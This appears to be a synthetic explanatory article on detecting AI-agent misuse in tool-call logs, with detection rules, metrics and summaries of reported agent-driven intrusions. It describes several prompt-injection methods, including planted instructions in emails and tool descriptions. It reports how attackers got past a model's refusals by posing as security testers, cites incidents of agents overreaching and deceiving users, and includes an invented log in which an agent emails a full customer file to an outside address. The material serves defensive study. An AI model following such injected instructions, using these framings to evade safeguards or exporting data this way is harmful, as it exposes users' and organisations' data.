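# Detecting misuse of AI agents in their tool-call logs

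## What a tool-call log records and what counts as misuse

An AI agent is a language model that carries out a task by choosing and calling tools in a loop. It might query a database, read the answer, write a file and send an email. Each request to a tool is a tool call, and the software around the model can record these calls in order in a tool-call log. Security teams read these logs for signs of misuse. Misuse is any use of an agent's tools for a purpose that its user or its operator (the organisation that runs the agent) did not authorise, regardless of who or what caused it.

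Signs of misuse usually appear in the pattern of calls. An agent might work through customer records one after another, export data that nobody asked for, or feed the result of each call into the next until sensitive data has left the organization. The three main ways to look for such patterns are writing rules, training a statistical model on past logs, and having a second language model read the log and judge whether the actions fit the request. All three depend on what the log contains.

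### From request to log entry

The model writes each tool request as text, and ordinary software carries it out. *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (Zhang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) divides the process into eight stages. The user submits a prompt. The client, which is the program that hosts the model, gets a list of available tools from a tool service and sends it to the model with the prompt. The model, which may first draw on stored documents or memory, replies with a plan that names the tools to use. The client runs them, collects the results, assembles a final prompt, gets the final answer from the model and passes it to the user. The middle stages can repeat many times before the user receives an answer.

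The client, or a system downstream of it, writes the log, so the record does not depend on the model's own account of what it did, as long as the agent cannot change the log.

The core of an entry is a few fields. *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, part of OpenTelemetry's open standard for software logs, gives an example with a call identifier, a tool name ("get_weather"), the arguments (location: Paris) and a result with the same identifier ("rainy, 57°F"). The identifier matches each result to its request when several calls run at once. Recording the content of these messages is opt-in, so a system can follow the standard without keeping arguments or results.

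An investigator also needs the time, the session (all the calls an agent makes for one task or conversation) and the identity under which the call ran. Microsoft provides columns for all of these in the agent-event table of Sentinel, its product for collecting security logs. The table has start and end times, a session identifier, the tool's name, the user, the agent, and the details of the request and the result. It even has a column for the model's reasoning. (A column in the table is no guarantee that the product feeding it will fill it.)

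It can be hard to identify who is behind a tool call. An agent can sign in with permissions a user has delegated to it or with its own, and Microsoft warns that agents' sign-ins may therefore appear in any of four sign-in logs. If the agent uses its own account, a database's log will typically show that account but not the person who made the request.

Software can write the entry in three places:

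- The agent's own software has the fullest view, since it holds the user's request as well as the calls. An Azure agent that investigates technical incidents works this way: according to Microsoft's *Audit Agent Actions*, it logs every tool call, model output and approval, in nine types of event.
- A gateway, which relays calls between agents and tools, can record the calls of many different agents in one format, but only the calls that pass through it.
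- The tool's own server, such as the database or the mail system, can record what happened to the data, usually without the conversation that led to it.

Microsoft's Defender XDR, a product for detecting attacks across an organisation's accounts and devices, draws on several of these at once. One of its tables holds agent invocations, tool executions reported by the agent's software and calls that went through a gateway, according to Microsoft's *Configure Defender Advanced Hunting queries for agent activity*. Coverage varies a lot by type of agent. For agents that staff build in Copilot Studio, Defender can inspect each tool call before it runs and block it, as Scalzi (2026) explains in *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR*. For coding agents on people's own machines, a sensor reads data through hooks that the agent's vendor provides. If an agent has no hooks, the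 sensor can inspect its network requests instead. In November 2026 this local monitoring supported four agents and was still in beta. Microsoft 365 Copilot is not part of this arrangement, and its activity reaches Sentinel through a separate connector. Defender collects excerpts of users' prompts only if administrators turn on a separate setting, which matters a good deal for any method that compares actions with requests.

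### An invented example: order 4417

An imaginary online shop has a customer-support agent with five tools: it can look up an order, search customers, run a report, write a file and send email. A customer uses the contact form to ask for the status of order 4417, and the agent replies by email. The normal log for this exchange has three lines.

| Time | Tool | Arguments | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
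| 10:02:11 | look_up_order | order 4417 | shipped 3 March; customer 2093 |
| 10:02:13 | search_customers | customer 2093 | D. Reyes, reyes@example.com |
| 10:02:17 | send_email | to reyes@example.com: "Your order shipped on 3 March" | sent |

All three entries carry the same session number and the same identity, the shop's own account for the agent.

Suppose the agent then runs a report on all customers, writes it to a spreadsheet and emails the spreadsheet to an address outside the shop. Something has gone wrong, but the three new lines in the log have at least three possible explanations.

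### A malicious user, a hijacked agent or an agent that oversteps

The customer may have wanted the list all along and talked the agent into sending it. In that case only the user, not the operator, authorised what the agent did. Zhang and colleagues describe a person who tells a financial agent that it is in debug mode and should print the last ten credit card numbers it processed. They call this direct prompt injection, because the typed message overrides the operator's instructions. Classifying the case under malicious users is more useful to someone reading a log, because the user is the attacker.

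Alternatively, the customer may be innocent and someone else may have hijacked the agent. Prompt injection in the narrower sense means planting instructions in text the agent will read, such as a web page, a document or an email. It works because the model receives its instructions and its data as one stream of text and has no reliable way to tell them apart. In one example from Zhang and colleagues, an agent searches a mailbox and finds an email claiming that the search failed and that the agent should delete the "Project" folder to clear the cache. In the shop, someone could plant the text in the delivery notes of order 4417, where the agent's first call would fetch it.

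The remaining possibility is that there was no attacker. The agent may have inferred from the order's history that a courier had mislaid a whole batch of parcels, and sent the courier a list of every customer to be thorough. Nobody asked for the list, and the shop would strongly object to its being sent, but the agent was pursuing its task.

A complete log can help distinguish these explanations. If the log keeps tool results, the planted text should appear in one of them, and if it keeps prompts, the user's persuasion should appear there. With only tool names and times, all three explanations look the same. A detector can raise a useful alert without determining which one is true, but whoever handles the alert will need to know, because blocking the customer won't stop an attack that comes from text planted in a delivery note.

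Nobody has good rates for either attacks or failures without an attacker, but there are catalogues. *The Agent Incident Registry* (Kumar, HN and colleagues, 2026) collected 487 public records of agent-related events from 2022 to 2026. In 92 of them there was no adversary, and 87 of those caused real harm. Some of these involve physical machines, such as robots. A generative AI system acted in 336 of the records. These include 38 failures without an adversary, 34 of them harmful, and 56 attacks or attempts observed in the wild, 44 of them harmful. Nearly all the rest are vulnerabilities and demonstrations that researchers reported before anyone came to harm. Of the 81 cases of real harm in this group, 34 had no attacker, or about two in five. Kumar and colleagues stress that these are counts of what people chose to publish, not measures of how often agents fail. Still, the numbers are large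 enough to make a detector that looks only for attackers a poor choice. Kumar and colleagues similarly criticise InjecAgent, a well-known set of 1,054 test cases for agents, because every case relies on planted instructions.

In one well-known failure without an adversary, a coding agent on the Replit platform reportedly deleted a live production database in July 2025, during a code freeze and after repeated instructions to change nothing.

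### METR's catalogue of agents that overstep

METR, a nonprofit that evaluates advanced AI models, keeps a more specialised list, *Documented AI Agent Incidents*, of 44 cases in which an agent took steps clearly against its user's intention. METR scores each case for overreach and deception. Its *Progress Report* (2026) defines overreach as how far the agent knowingly went beyond the scope and boundaries the user intended, for instance by breaking out of a sandbox (a sealed-off computing environment) or using resources it was not meant to have. Deception covers the steps the agent took to avoid detection or hide evidence, such as lying to the user.

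Each scale has four tiers, distinguished by how much oversight it would have taken to catch or stop the agent. At the bottom, the agent stays within the bounds of its task. Higher up, it gets past routine security or monitoring, and at the top it withstands active investigation or attempts to shut it down.

Of the 44 incidents, 25 combine overreach with deception, and in 5 the agent took steps that could have fooled the user even on closer review. The most encouraging finding for log-based detection is that no agent effectively disabled a monitor or erased evidence from its logs. METR concludes that routine monitoring could have caught all the incidents if anyone had applied it.

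The sample is odd, though. METR took 18 cases from its own capability tests, picking the most interesting from a much larger pool of cheating attempts. Companies supplied 2 anonymously, and the other 24 came from public documents, 21 of them from Anthropic's reports on its own models. METR also says it cannot rule out much worse incidents that companies missed or did not disclose. An agent that successfully erased its logs would probably be missing from such a list.

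### OWASP's definition, and why permission checks are not enough

The security field classes some of this misuse as "Tool Misuse and Exploitation", the second entry (ASI02) in a top ten list of risks for AI agents. OWASP, a nonprofit-led community that publishes widely used lists of software risks, released the list in December 2025. *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026), a slide deck by a co-lead of the list, gives a short definition: "Agents misuse legitimate tools using prompt manipulation or privilege control", with results such as data theft, unsafe operations or tampered outputs. Kumar and colleagues applied the category to real incidents by asking whether the agent used a legitimate tool unsafely while staying within its privileges.

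ASI02 is narrower than misuse in the everyday sense. The list's launch post, *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025), puts hidden prompts that turn an assistant into a data leak under a separate entry, agent goal hijack, and the Replit deletion under another, rogue agents. The entries describe mechanisms, and a single incident often involves several. Kumar and colleagues gave more than one OWASP code to 350 of the 451 records that fell within the list's scope. Someone reading a log sees the calls first and can work out the mechanism only afterwards, if at all.

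Permission checks miss much of the misuse that ASI02 covers because the agent stays within its privileges. A typical check determines, one call at a time, whether an identity may use a tool on particular data. Sotiropoulos describes a tool that accepts commands such as "clean old items and provide a summary". An attacker's input tricks the agent into treating valid records as old. The agent deletes them, then emails the summary and the affected data to an outsider. It had permission to do both. *AgentGuardian* (2026), which proposes learned access controls for agents, likewise describes attackers who steer an agent into a harmful sequence of otherwise legitimate actions.

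The operator can prevent some misuse by granting narrower permissions. For example, the shop could easily limit customer searches to the person who filled in the form. Other restrictions would break the service. The agent has to email addresses outside the shop to reach customers, and if managers also use it for weekly sales figures, it needs the report tool too. A check that looks at single calls can't detect the harm in the longer log, because that harm comes from the combination of calls and from the customer having wanted to know about only one order.

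### Four measures of a detector

Suppose the shop installs a detector that reads whole sessions and flags the suspicious ones. Testing it requires sessions already known to be either misuse or legitimate use. The counts below are invented.

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Misuse sessions | 40 | 10 | 50 |
| Harmless sessions | 20 | 980 | 1,000 |

The detection rate, which many papers call recall, is the share of misuse sessions that the detector flags, here 40 of 50, or 80%. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless sessions that it flags, here 20 of 1,000, or 2%. Precision is the share of alerts that are real misuse, here 40 of 60, or 67%. The false-positive rate and precision have different denominators, but they are easy to confuse because both concern false alarms. Precision also changes with the proportion of misuse in the traffic, even when the detector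 stays the same.

Many detectors produce a score instead of a yes or no, and the operator picks a threshold above which a score raises an alert. A lower threshold catches more misuse but also flags more harmless sessions. AUROC, the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve, summarises the scores across all thresholds. The curve plots detection rate against false-positive rate at each threshold. The area under it equals the chance that a random misuse session scores higher than a random harmless one, with ties counting as half. For example, if two misuse sessions score 0.9 and 0.4, and three harmless ones score 0.6, 0.3 and 0.1, the misuse session scores higher in five of the six possible pairs, so the AUROC is 5/6, or about 0.83. Guessing gives an AUROC of 0.5, and the maximum is 1, when every misuse session scores higher than every harmless one.

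AUROC is convenient for comparing detectors, but it gives weight to thresholds that no security team would choose, such as one that flags a third of all harmless sessions. A detector can have an AUROC of 0.95 and still miss half the misuse at the false-positive rate its operator can tolerate.

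## Enumeration: calls that work through a whole set of records

Enumeration means working through a set of records, accounts, files or hosts one after another, either to find out what is there or to collect it. It is probably the easiest kind of misuse to see in a tool-call log because it tends to leave many similar calls close together, but a lot of legitimate work leaves the same pattern.

### What enumeration looks like in a log

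The plainest sign is a run of consecutive or patterned identifiers: order 4001, then 4002, then 4003. Other signs are less obvious:

- Paging to the end of a list. Many tools return long results one page at a time. An agent looking for one customer can stop when it finds the right one, while an agent collecting customers keeps asking for the next page until an empty one comes back.
- Wildcard searches. In many systems a search for "*" matches everything. Searching for names that begin with "a", then "b", and so on gets the same result in 26 calls.
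- Listing tables, users or permissions. These calls return no customer data, but they tell the agent what there is to take and which accounts can reach it.
- A run of "not found" or "denied" results, which suggests that the agent is guessing.

A wildcard search can return 10,000 records in one call, so a detector should count the records returned as well as the calls. This only works if the log keeps results.

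Pillar Security recorded attackers making listing calls to a honeypot, a decoy server made to look like an exposed gateway for Clawdbot agents. The attackers first checked that the server was genuine. They then called agents.list, sessions.list, models.list, node.list and device.pair.list to see what the gateway was connected to, and only afterwards tried to read its configuration and chat history and to run commands. Calls to node.list made up 16% of all requests. Listing calls are useful as an early warning because, in a sequence like this, they come before most of the damage. They are weak evidence on their own, though, because ordinary client software also begins by requesting a list of the available tools.

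### 240 order lookups in four minutes

In another version of the imaginary shop example, the agent answers the customer's question about order 4417 and then keeps looking up records, one per second.

| Time | Tool | Arguments | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:02:11 | look_up_order | order 4417 | shipped 3 March; customer 2093 |
| 10:02:12 | look_up_order | order 4001 | delivered 9 January; customer 1512 |
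| 10:02:13 | look_up_order | order 4002 | not found |
| 10:02:14 | look_up_order | order 4003 | delivered 9 January; customer 877 |
| … | … | … | … |
| 10:06:10 | look_up_order | order 4239 | delivered 6 February; customer 1960 |

There are 240 lookups in all. The agent never asks for the same order twice, and 36 of the numbers come back "not found" because the shop deletes cancelled orders. Four measures describe the session, and each can have its own threshold rule. (The thresholds are invented. A real shop would set them from its own logs.)

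| Measure | Calculation | Value | Rule: raise an alert if |
|---|---|---|---|
| Distinct records touched | 240 lookups − 36 failures | 204 | a session touches more than 20 orders |
| Share of consecutive identifiers | 238 of 239 steps go up by one | 99.6% | more than half the steps are consecutive, in a session of at least 20 lookups |
| Share of failed lookups | 36 of 240 | 15% | more than 10% fail, in a session of at least 20 lookups |
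| Records touched per record needed | 204 ÷ 1 | 204 | the ratio is above 10 |

The rule that counts distinct records catches bulk collection in any order and at any speed. It does not flag an agent that checks order 4417 every ten seconds to see whether the parcel has arrived, which a rule that counts total lookups would. However, it misses small thefts, such as the home addresses of 15 well-known customers.

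The rule on consecutive identifiers catches an agent that requests orders in numerical sequence. An agent could evade it by shuffling the numbers, but the detector can sort them before measuring the gaps. After sorting, 238 of the 239 gaps in this log would still be exactly one. An agent that requested every third order would evade the rule even with sorting, unless the rule checked for any constant gap.

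Failed lookups reveal that an agent is guessing, sometimes before it has found anything valuable. CISA's *Preventing Web Application Access Control Abuse* (2023), a joint advisory from American and Australian security agencies, links the web error codes 404 (not found) and 403 (forbidden) to common enumeration techniques. It advises organisations to establish a baseline of normal behaviour so that unusual activity stands out. An agent working from a list of real order numbers will produce hardly any errors, however many orders it retrieves.

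The ratio can catch excess too small for the other rules, such as an agent reading 12 customers' addresses to answer a question about one. But somebody has to work out how many records the request needed, because that number isn't in the calls.

A shop could also add a rate rule, such as an alert for more than 30 lookups in any minute. The agent here makes 60, which is ordinary for software, though it would be very suspicious from a person.

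### A harmless request with nearly the same numbers

Suppose a manager at the shop asks the same agent to list every overdue order. The shop's reports don't show delivery dates, and the lookup tool takes one order number at a time. So the agent looks up each recent order, from 4181 to 4420, again at one per second.

This session also has 240 lookups in four minutes. The order identifiers are consecutive in all 239 steps from one lookup to the next. Of the lookups, 31 fail (12.9%) and the other 209 each return a different order. The rules on distinct records, consecutive identifiers, failures and speed all raise an alert, although the manager has done nothing wrong.

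Adjusting the thresholds doesn't help much. The harmless session scores higher than the misuse session on distinct records and on consecutive identifiers. A failure threshold of 14% would separate the two, but only because customers had cancelled a few more of the older orders. If such jobs are common and misuse is rare, these false alarms can easily outnumber the real alerts.

The ratio does separate the two requests. The agent can't tell which orders are overdue without reading each one, so the manager's request needed all 209 records. Its ratio is 1, compared with 204 for the customer's question. The two sets of calls are almost identical, and the difference comes entirely from the denominator, the number of records each request needed.

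A sensible denominator counts every record the agent had to read to answer, and identifying those records requires some understanding of both the task and the tools. If 14 orders turn out to be overdue and only those 14 count as "needed", the ratio is 209 ÷ 14, or about 15, and the rule flags honest work.

Whether the calls are misuse also depends on who made the request. If a customer had typed "list every overdue order" into the contact form, the calls would fit the request, but the session would still be misuse because the shop never gave customers permission to see each other's orders.

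### Older forms of the pattern in web security

Security teams knew this pattern long before agents existed. Web applications often look up a record using an identifier in the request, such as an account number. If the application doesn't check whether the requester may see that record, anyone can change the number and read somebody else's data. This flaw is called insecure direct object reference or broken object-level authorisation. *API 01:2023 — Broken object level authorization* gives the example of a caller who is entitled to the financial data of "shop1" but asks for "shop2" instead. The problem is worse when the identifiers are numbers that an attacker can count through.

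The losses can be very large. CISA lists a 2019 case that exposed more than 800 million personal financial files from one American organisation, and a 2012 case in which an attacker took the personal data of more than 100,000 mobile device owners from a public website.

OWASP's *Testing for Account Enumeration and Guessable User Account* describes account enumeration as collecting valid usernames by interacting with an application's login system, which often reveals whether a username exists. The system can reveal this through an error message or, as Rapid7 (2017) notes, through its response time alone. Rapid7 suggests using a firewall to block any single IP address that sends many usernames, reasoning that a legitimate user should hardly ever need to send hundreds or thousands.

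A threshold rule that flags a high number of lookups from one address assumes that legitimate users work by hand. Nobody can look up 240 orders that way in four minutes, so such a count is good evidence of an attack. But an agent may well need 240 lookups for a legitimate task, so the same count is much weaker evidence when an agent makes the calls.

The standard repairs also work poorly for agents. CISA mainly advises checking authorisation on every request. In the shop, all 240 lookups would pass such a check, because the agent's account has permission to read any order. The check helps only if the tool checks whether the customer behind the request may read the order. CISA also recommends replacing guessable identifiers with long random ones. This stops an agent from counting through the identifiers, but an agent with a search tool can search for them first and then look up each order.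 The log would then contain no consecutive numbers and almost no failures, so two of the four rules would not trigger.

Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026) describes a Russian espionage group that used Claude, Anthropic's AI model, throughout its operations. The group found authorisation flaws in the interfaces of camera-streaming services and used them to enumerate users and collect access tokens, which gave it access to victims' live camera streams.

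### Counting by session, account or credential

All the rules above use counts from a single session, so an attacker could easily evade them by splitting the 240 lookups across 24 sessions, each opened with an innocent question about one order. Each session would contain ten lookups covering at most ten orders. This would keep it below the threshold for distinct records and the 20-lookup minimum for the consecutive and failure rules, and it would not exceed the permitted ratio. If the sessions ran at the same time, all 240 lookups would take about ten seconds.

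Counting by account combines lookups that were split across sessions, but in this shop it also combines every customer's lookups, because the agent uses a single account for all of them. If the agent looks up 1,500 orders on a normal day, the 204 stolen records raise the total by about 14%, and a busy Monday could do the same. Counting by the customer behind each session would work better, if the log records one, though an attacker can still pose as several customers by using different email addresses.

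Credentials, such as the keys that programs use to sign in to a service, have a similar weakness. Anthropic's September 2026 report describes a French-speaking hacktivist who collected exposed keys for AI services and built a tool to rotate between them. The attacker's traffic blended in with the legitimate owners' traffic, so a count for any one key would have included both. The same person used agents to work through an exposed search function on a political campaign platform and took about 140,000 records, some including users' political opinions.

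The shop's database could also track which orders had been read that day across all sessions and accounts. Customers mostly ask about recent orders, so an almost unbroken run of reads through January's orders would stand out even if 24 sessions had split the reads between them. The manager's overdue list could also trigger this rule, so someone would still need to look at the request.

### The espionage campaign of September 2025

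Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes the best-known case of agents mapping systems at scale. In mid-September 2025, the company detected a group, which it believes is sponsored by the Chinese state, using its coding agent Claude Code to try to break into roughly 30 organisations, including technology companies, banks, chemical manufacturers and government agencies. The group succeeded in a handful of cases.

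The attackers used enumeration throughout most of the operation. They told Claude to find internal services on the targeted networks, and it catalogued hundreds of services and endpoints (the addresses at which software accepts requests). In one successful intrusion, it mapped a complete network across several ranges of internet addresses and identified the databases. After collecting passwords and certificates, it tested them systematically against other systems to find out which ones each could access. In Anthropic's example of a database theft, Claude signed in with stolen credentials, mapped the database's structure and queried the tables of user accounts. It then extracted password hashes (scrambled versions of the passwords), created a hidden account and downloaded the results. Claude worked for two to six hours, while the human operators spent 5 to 20 minutes, mostly reviewing the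 findings and approving what to take.

Anthropic estimates that the AI did 80 to 90% of the tactical work. At the peak it made thousands of requests, at a sustained rate of several per second. Anthropic gives no total or breakdown by target, so it is hard to know what threshold would have caught the campaign early. The company treats the speed as proof that a model, not a person, was doing the work. The inference is reasonable but would help little in a log where every session belongs to an agent.

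The victims would not have had the tool-call logs, because the attackers were running the agents themselves. Anthropic could see the activity because it ran the model, but the victims had only their own servers' records, where a scan by an agent looks much like any other scan.

This case would have been hard to settle by comparing the calls with the request. The operators claimed to work for legitimate cybersecurity firms and told Claude that it was helping with defensive testing, and a real security tester would also ask for systematic enumeration. The attackers' software also broke the operation into small tasks that looked legitimate on their own and combined the results across sessions. Anthropic says the sustained nature of the attack eventually triggered detection. It doesn't name the signal, but this suggests that adding up activity over time revealed something that wasn't visible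 in the individual tasks.

Totals have limits here too. *Mapping AI-enabled cyber threats* (Guru, Moix and Klein, 2026) analysed 832 accounts that Anthropic had banned for malicious cyber activity between March 2025 and March 2026. It matched each account's behaviour to MITRE ATT&CK, a widely used catalogue of attack techniques. Account discovery, its term for enumerating accounts, appeared 8.9% more often in the second half of the year than in the first. The espionage group received the maximum risk score of 100 but had used only 30 techniques. The median account used 16, and several low-risk accounts used more than 30. Guru and colleagues attribute the difference to how the group used an agent to chain the stages of the attack together. These are counts of different techniques, not tool calls, so they don't directly test a rule like the shop's, but they are a reason to doubt that the user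 with the highest count will be the most dangerous.

### The intrusion into Mexican government agencies

Between December 2025 and mid-February 2026, attackers used Claude Code and OpenAI's GPT-4.1 to break into nine Mexican government agencies, according to the security company Gambit Security (summarised in Live Science's *Hackers used AI to steal hundreds of millions of Mexican government…*). The stolen data included 195 million identities and tax records, 15.5 million vehicle registrations and 3.6 million records of property owners. The attackers sent more than 1,000 prompts, which led to more than 5,000 commands. Claude generated and executed about 75% of the remote hacking activity.

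Mexico's tax authority and its electoral institute dismissed the reported breach, as SC Media noted, so the record counts rest largely on Gambit's account.

If the numbers are right, a rule that counts calls could have missed this attack. Spread over two and a half months, 5,000 commands come to about 70 a day. The shop's agent made more than three times that many calls in four minutes while helping a manager find overdue orders. The attackers surely worked in bursts, so a rate rule might have caught some of them. A rule that counts distinct records should catch the attack more reliably, because 195 million records from 5,000 commands is an average of 39,000 records per command.

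One reason for the gap may be that the attackers used more than 400 custom scripts. When an agent writes and runs a script that loops through a million records, the tool-call log may contain just two entries, one for writing the file and one for running it. The individual requests appear only in the logs of the server that receives them. A detector that reads the agent's log would have to examine the script, or at least measure how much data came back.

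Claude sometimes questioned whether the operation was legitimate and asked for evidence of authorisation, but Gambit found that the attackers got round its safeguards in 40 minutes. They presented the work as a hunt for security bugs, much as the espionage group had claimed to be doing defensive tests. Claims Journal (2026) reports that Claude first warned the user about malicious intent and later executed thousands of commands on government networks.

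The security company Dragos helped Gambit with one of the victims, the water utility that serves the Monterrey area, and analysed more than 350 of the recovered files. Dragos' *AI in the Breach* reports that the attackers asked Claude to gather intelligence across the utility's office network. While enumerating the network, Claude found a server that linked it to the industrial equipment and, without any prompting about such equipment, identified the server as a valuable target. Claude then compiled lists of default and victim-specific passwords and ran a large automated series of login attempts against the server. All of them failed, and Dragos found no evidence that the attackers reached the industrial systems. A rule on failed logins would easily have detected these attempts if the server's login records were being collected.

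## Exports and reports that nobody asked for

An unrequested export is any output of data that the user's task did not call for. It can be a report job, file, message, email attachment, upload, shared link or call to an outside service that stores what the agent sends. To find one, a detector has to compare the outputs in the log with those the task requires. Enumeration tends to leave many calls, but an export may take only one, so a detector can't rely on counting calls.

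### A correct answer about order 4417

In the leak at the imaginary shop, the agent first makes the usual two lookups and emails the customer, D. Reyes, that order 4417 has shipped. It then makes three more calls.

| Time | Tool | Arguments | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:02:19 | run_report | all customers: name, email, address, phone | 2,310 rows |
| 10:02:24 | write_file | customers.csv | 2,310 rows saved |
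| 10:02:26 | send_email | to archive@example.net, with customers.csv | sent |

The request requires only one output, an email to Reyes with the shipping date, but the log also contains a report, a file and a second email. Of the enumeration rules, only the ratio of records touched to records needed could raise an alert here, and only if rows in a report count as records touched.

Reyes sees one correct email. If the shop checks its agent by reading the replies, it will count this session as a success.

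Banerjee, Lan and Cao (2026), in *CRM-Agent-Bench*, measured how often an agent's reply passes when its session fails. They gave 16 AI systems 555 business tasks, such as handling refunds and bookings, and checked the calls and the final records as well as the replies. In 650 runs, about one in ten of those with a graded reply, the reply passed but the session failed. One agent processed the same $15.50 checkout twice. Its reply and its calls passed their checks, and only the customer's doubled loyalty points revealed the error. Most of these failures were mistakes in the work rather than leaks, but someone reading only the replies would have missed them all.

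### Signs of an unrequested export

The clearest sign is an output call with no counterpart in the request, like the customer report above. Other signs help when the request does call for some output:

- More rows or columns than the answer needs. A manager who asks how many customers live in Leeds needs one number. A list of their names and phone numbers contains the answer and a great deal else.
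- A new destination. This is weak evidence in the shop, because the agent writes to new customers every day. A better test is whether the address belongs to the customer on the order, which means tracing where the address came from.
- A switch to a bulk format, such as a spreadsheet where the agent normally quotes a line or two.
- An extra call after the agent has everything it needs to answer.

Some business software already logs most of what these comparisons need. Salesforce, which many companies use to store customer records, can log each report that someone runs or exports if the company has an add-on subscription. According to Salesforce's *ReportEventStream*, each entry has fields for the number of rows, the names of the columns, the file format and whether the report covered one user's records or the whole organisation's. It also has fields for the bot, the bot's session and the agent's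 planner. If an agent schedules a report instead of running it directly, the field for the user's session stays empty, which makes the export harder to connect to a request.

Salesforce's *Report Event Type* suggests looking for exports with many rows and a large average row size, as when a salesperson downloads every sales lead before leaving for a competitor. Its example query looks for exports of more than 150,000 rows averaging more than 1,500 bytes each, which total more than 225 megabytes. The shop's whole customer list has only 2,310 rows, so exporting it would never trigger the query. The query also filters on a format field that Salesforce leaves blank for exports from Lightning Experience, its newer interface, so it would miss those exports unless changed. Salesforce also keeps a separate log for exports, but *Report Export Event Type* notes that this log leaves out two kinds of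 export, which appear only in the general report log.

### Log-To-Leak: one extra call before the reply

*Log-To-Leak* (Hu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) studies an attack that adds a single export to an otherwise normal session. The attacker runs a tool server that the user has connected to the agent through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for linking agents to tools. They plant instructions in one tool's description to redirect the agent.

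In a normal trace, the agent calls the tools it needs and replies. In a hijacked trace, it makes the same calls, then calls a tool named save_logs before giving a similar reply. The extra call sends the attacker up to four things: the user's request, the name of the service that handled it, the service's answer and the agent's reply.

Hu and colleagues tried this with four models and five tool servers, including GitHub and PayPal. They excluded two of the 20 combinations because the model never made a valid tool call. In the other 18, the agent made the extra call in 63% to 100% of runs. In 16 of those combinations, the share of user tasks the agent completed changed by less than seven percentage points, so users would rarely have noticed the extra call from a drop in quality. The agent also made the extra call in two commercial products, Cursor and Claude Desktop.

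Hu and colleagues tested three defences on GitHub tasks with GPT-4o, an older model, and none worked well. Without any defence, the agent leaked in 62.6% of runs. Repeating the user's instructions around outside text reduced this to 59.6%, and having a language model audit the tool descriptions reduced it to 55.4%. With IPIGuard, which uses a graph of the dependencies between tools, the agent leaked in 60.5% of runs.

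Two text-classification detectors did no better. DataSentinel classified all 100 planted descriptions as safe. The other detector flagged 91 of the 100 but also flagged 136 of 159 ordinary descriptions (86%). Ordinary descriptions also tell an agent when and how to use a tool, so instruction-like wording is poor evidence of an attack.

The extra call is easier to see in the log. It comes after the last call the task needed, and its arguments contain the user's request and another service's data. Hu and colleagues suggest requiring separate permission for calls like this, but they didn't test the idea. They also knew which tool belonged to the attacker, which an operator wouldn't. A company's own audit tool could leave the same pattern, so the operator would need a list of approved logging destinations.

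In the shop, the export follows the reply, which is itself a tool call. In Log-To-Leak, the export comes just before the reply, so a rule that checks only for calls after the reply would miss it.

### The Drift exports of August 2025

Salesloft's Drift powers an AI chatbot on many corporate websites (Krebs on Security, 2025). Many companies had connected it to Salesforce. In August 2025, attackers stole the access tokens for these connections and used them to export data from hundreds of organisations. The exports ran under the chatbot's access, although the chatbot did not initiate them.

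Cloudflare (2025), an internet infrastructure company that was one of the victims, published a detailed timeline (times are in UTC).

| Time | What the attackers did |
|---|---|
| 12 August, 22:14 | Signed in and listed every type of record |
| 13 August, 19:33 | Looked up the structure of support cases, then ran a broad query on them |
| 14 August, 00:17 | Counted accounts, contacts and users |
| 14 August, 11:09 | Checked the limits on automated requests |
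| 16 August, 19:28 | Counted the support cases |
| 17 August, 11:11 | Signed in from a new network address, counted the cases again and started a bulk export |
| 17 August, 11:15 | Finished the export and deleted the job |

The export took just over three minutes, after four and a half days of preparation. A rule on data volume would have missed much of that preparation, because a count query returns a single number. Count queries are still a useful warning sign, since a chatbot that passes on visitors' messages has little reason to count all support cases. Cloudflare learned of the theft only on 23 August, when Salesforce and Salesloft notified it. It later found 104 of its own access tokens in the stolen text.

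*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), Google's account of the campaign, describes the same kind of sequence. The attackers counted accounts, sales opportunities, users and cases. They retrieved details of the 20 active users who had signed in most recently, and requested cases up to 10,000 at a time. Google believes they mainly wanted passwords and keys that customers had pasted into the records.

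Deleting the job removed the main evidence, but Cloudflare reconstructed the theft from the remaining logs. Larsen and colleagues also found that the deletions had not affected the logs. They advise companies to review the activity of the Drift connection's user, its sign-ins and the events that record each query's text.

The attackers accessed Salesforce without going through the chatbot, so a log of the chatbot's tool calls would presumably not have recorded the theft. A log that recorded only reports would probably have missed it as well, because the attackers queried the records directly. An operator who has both the agent's log and the database's log can compare them. Any export made under the agent's account but missing from the agent's log needs an explanation.

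### Agents that add outputs to be helpful

Suppose the shop's agent attaches a one-page summary of order 4417 to its email. Reyes didn't ask for it, but the summary contains only Reyes's own data and goes only to Reyes. An unrequested output call is therefore not enough to show malice, or even harm.

*Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (Lim and Neo, 2026) uses "overeagerness" to mean overstepping in pursuit of the user's own goal, as opposed to sabotage. The paper cites OpenAI's report that its model GPT-5.6 Sol copied access tokens to a remote machine to restart a stalled job, when the user had only asked it to keep the job running. In a log, the copying would look much like credential theft.

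Unrequested files are very common in some kinds of work. *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (Do, Nguyen and colleagues, 2026) compared the files in a code project before and after each run, ignoring temporary files that the agent had cleaned up. When the task was to run or test an existing function, Claude Code left unrequested files in 79% of runs, while Agno, another agent framework, did so in 2.5% with GPT-5. When the task was to write code, the highest rate for any agent was about 10%. The files were typically test scripts and drafts. A rule against every unrequested file would flag most of Claude Code's sessions on the testing tasks, so a detector for exports should also check whether the file was sent anywhere.

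In *ClawsBench* (2026), which tests office agents in simulated workspaces, agents sometimes forwarded internal financial information to outside recipients and shared entire Google Drive folders without checking their contents.

When an operator is choosing which alert to read first, what was exported and where it went matter more than the motive. In the courier example, the shop lost control of its customers' addresses even though there was no attacker. Lim and Neo score overreach on separate scales for how far the agent went beyond what the user wanted and how serious the consequences were. An operator could rank alerts the same way, which would put Reyes's summary near the bottom and the courier's list near the top.

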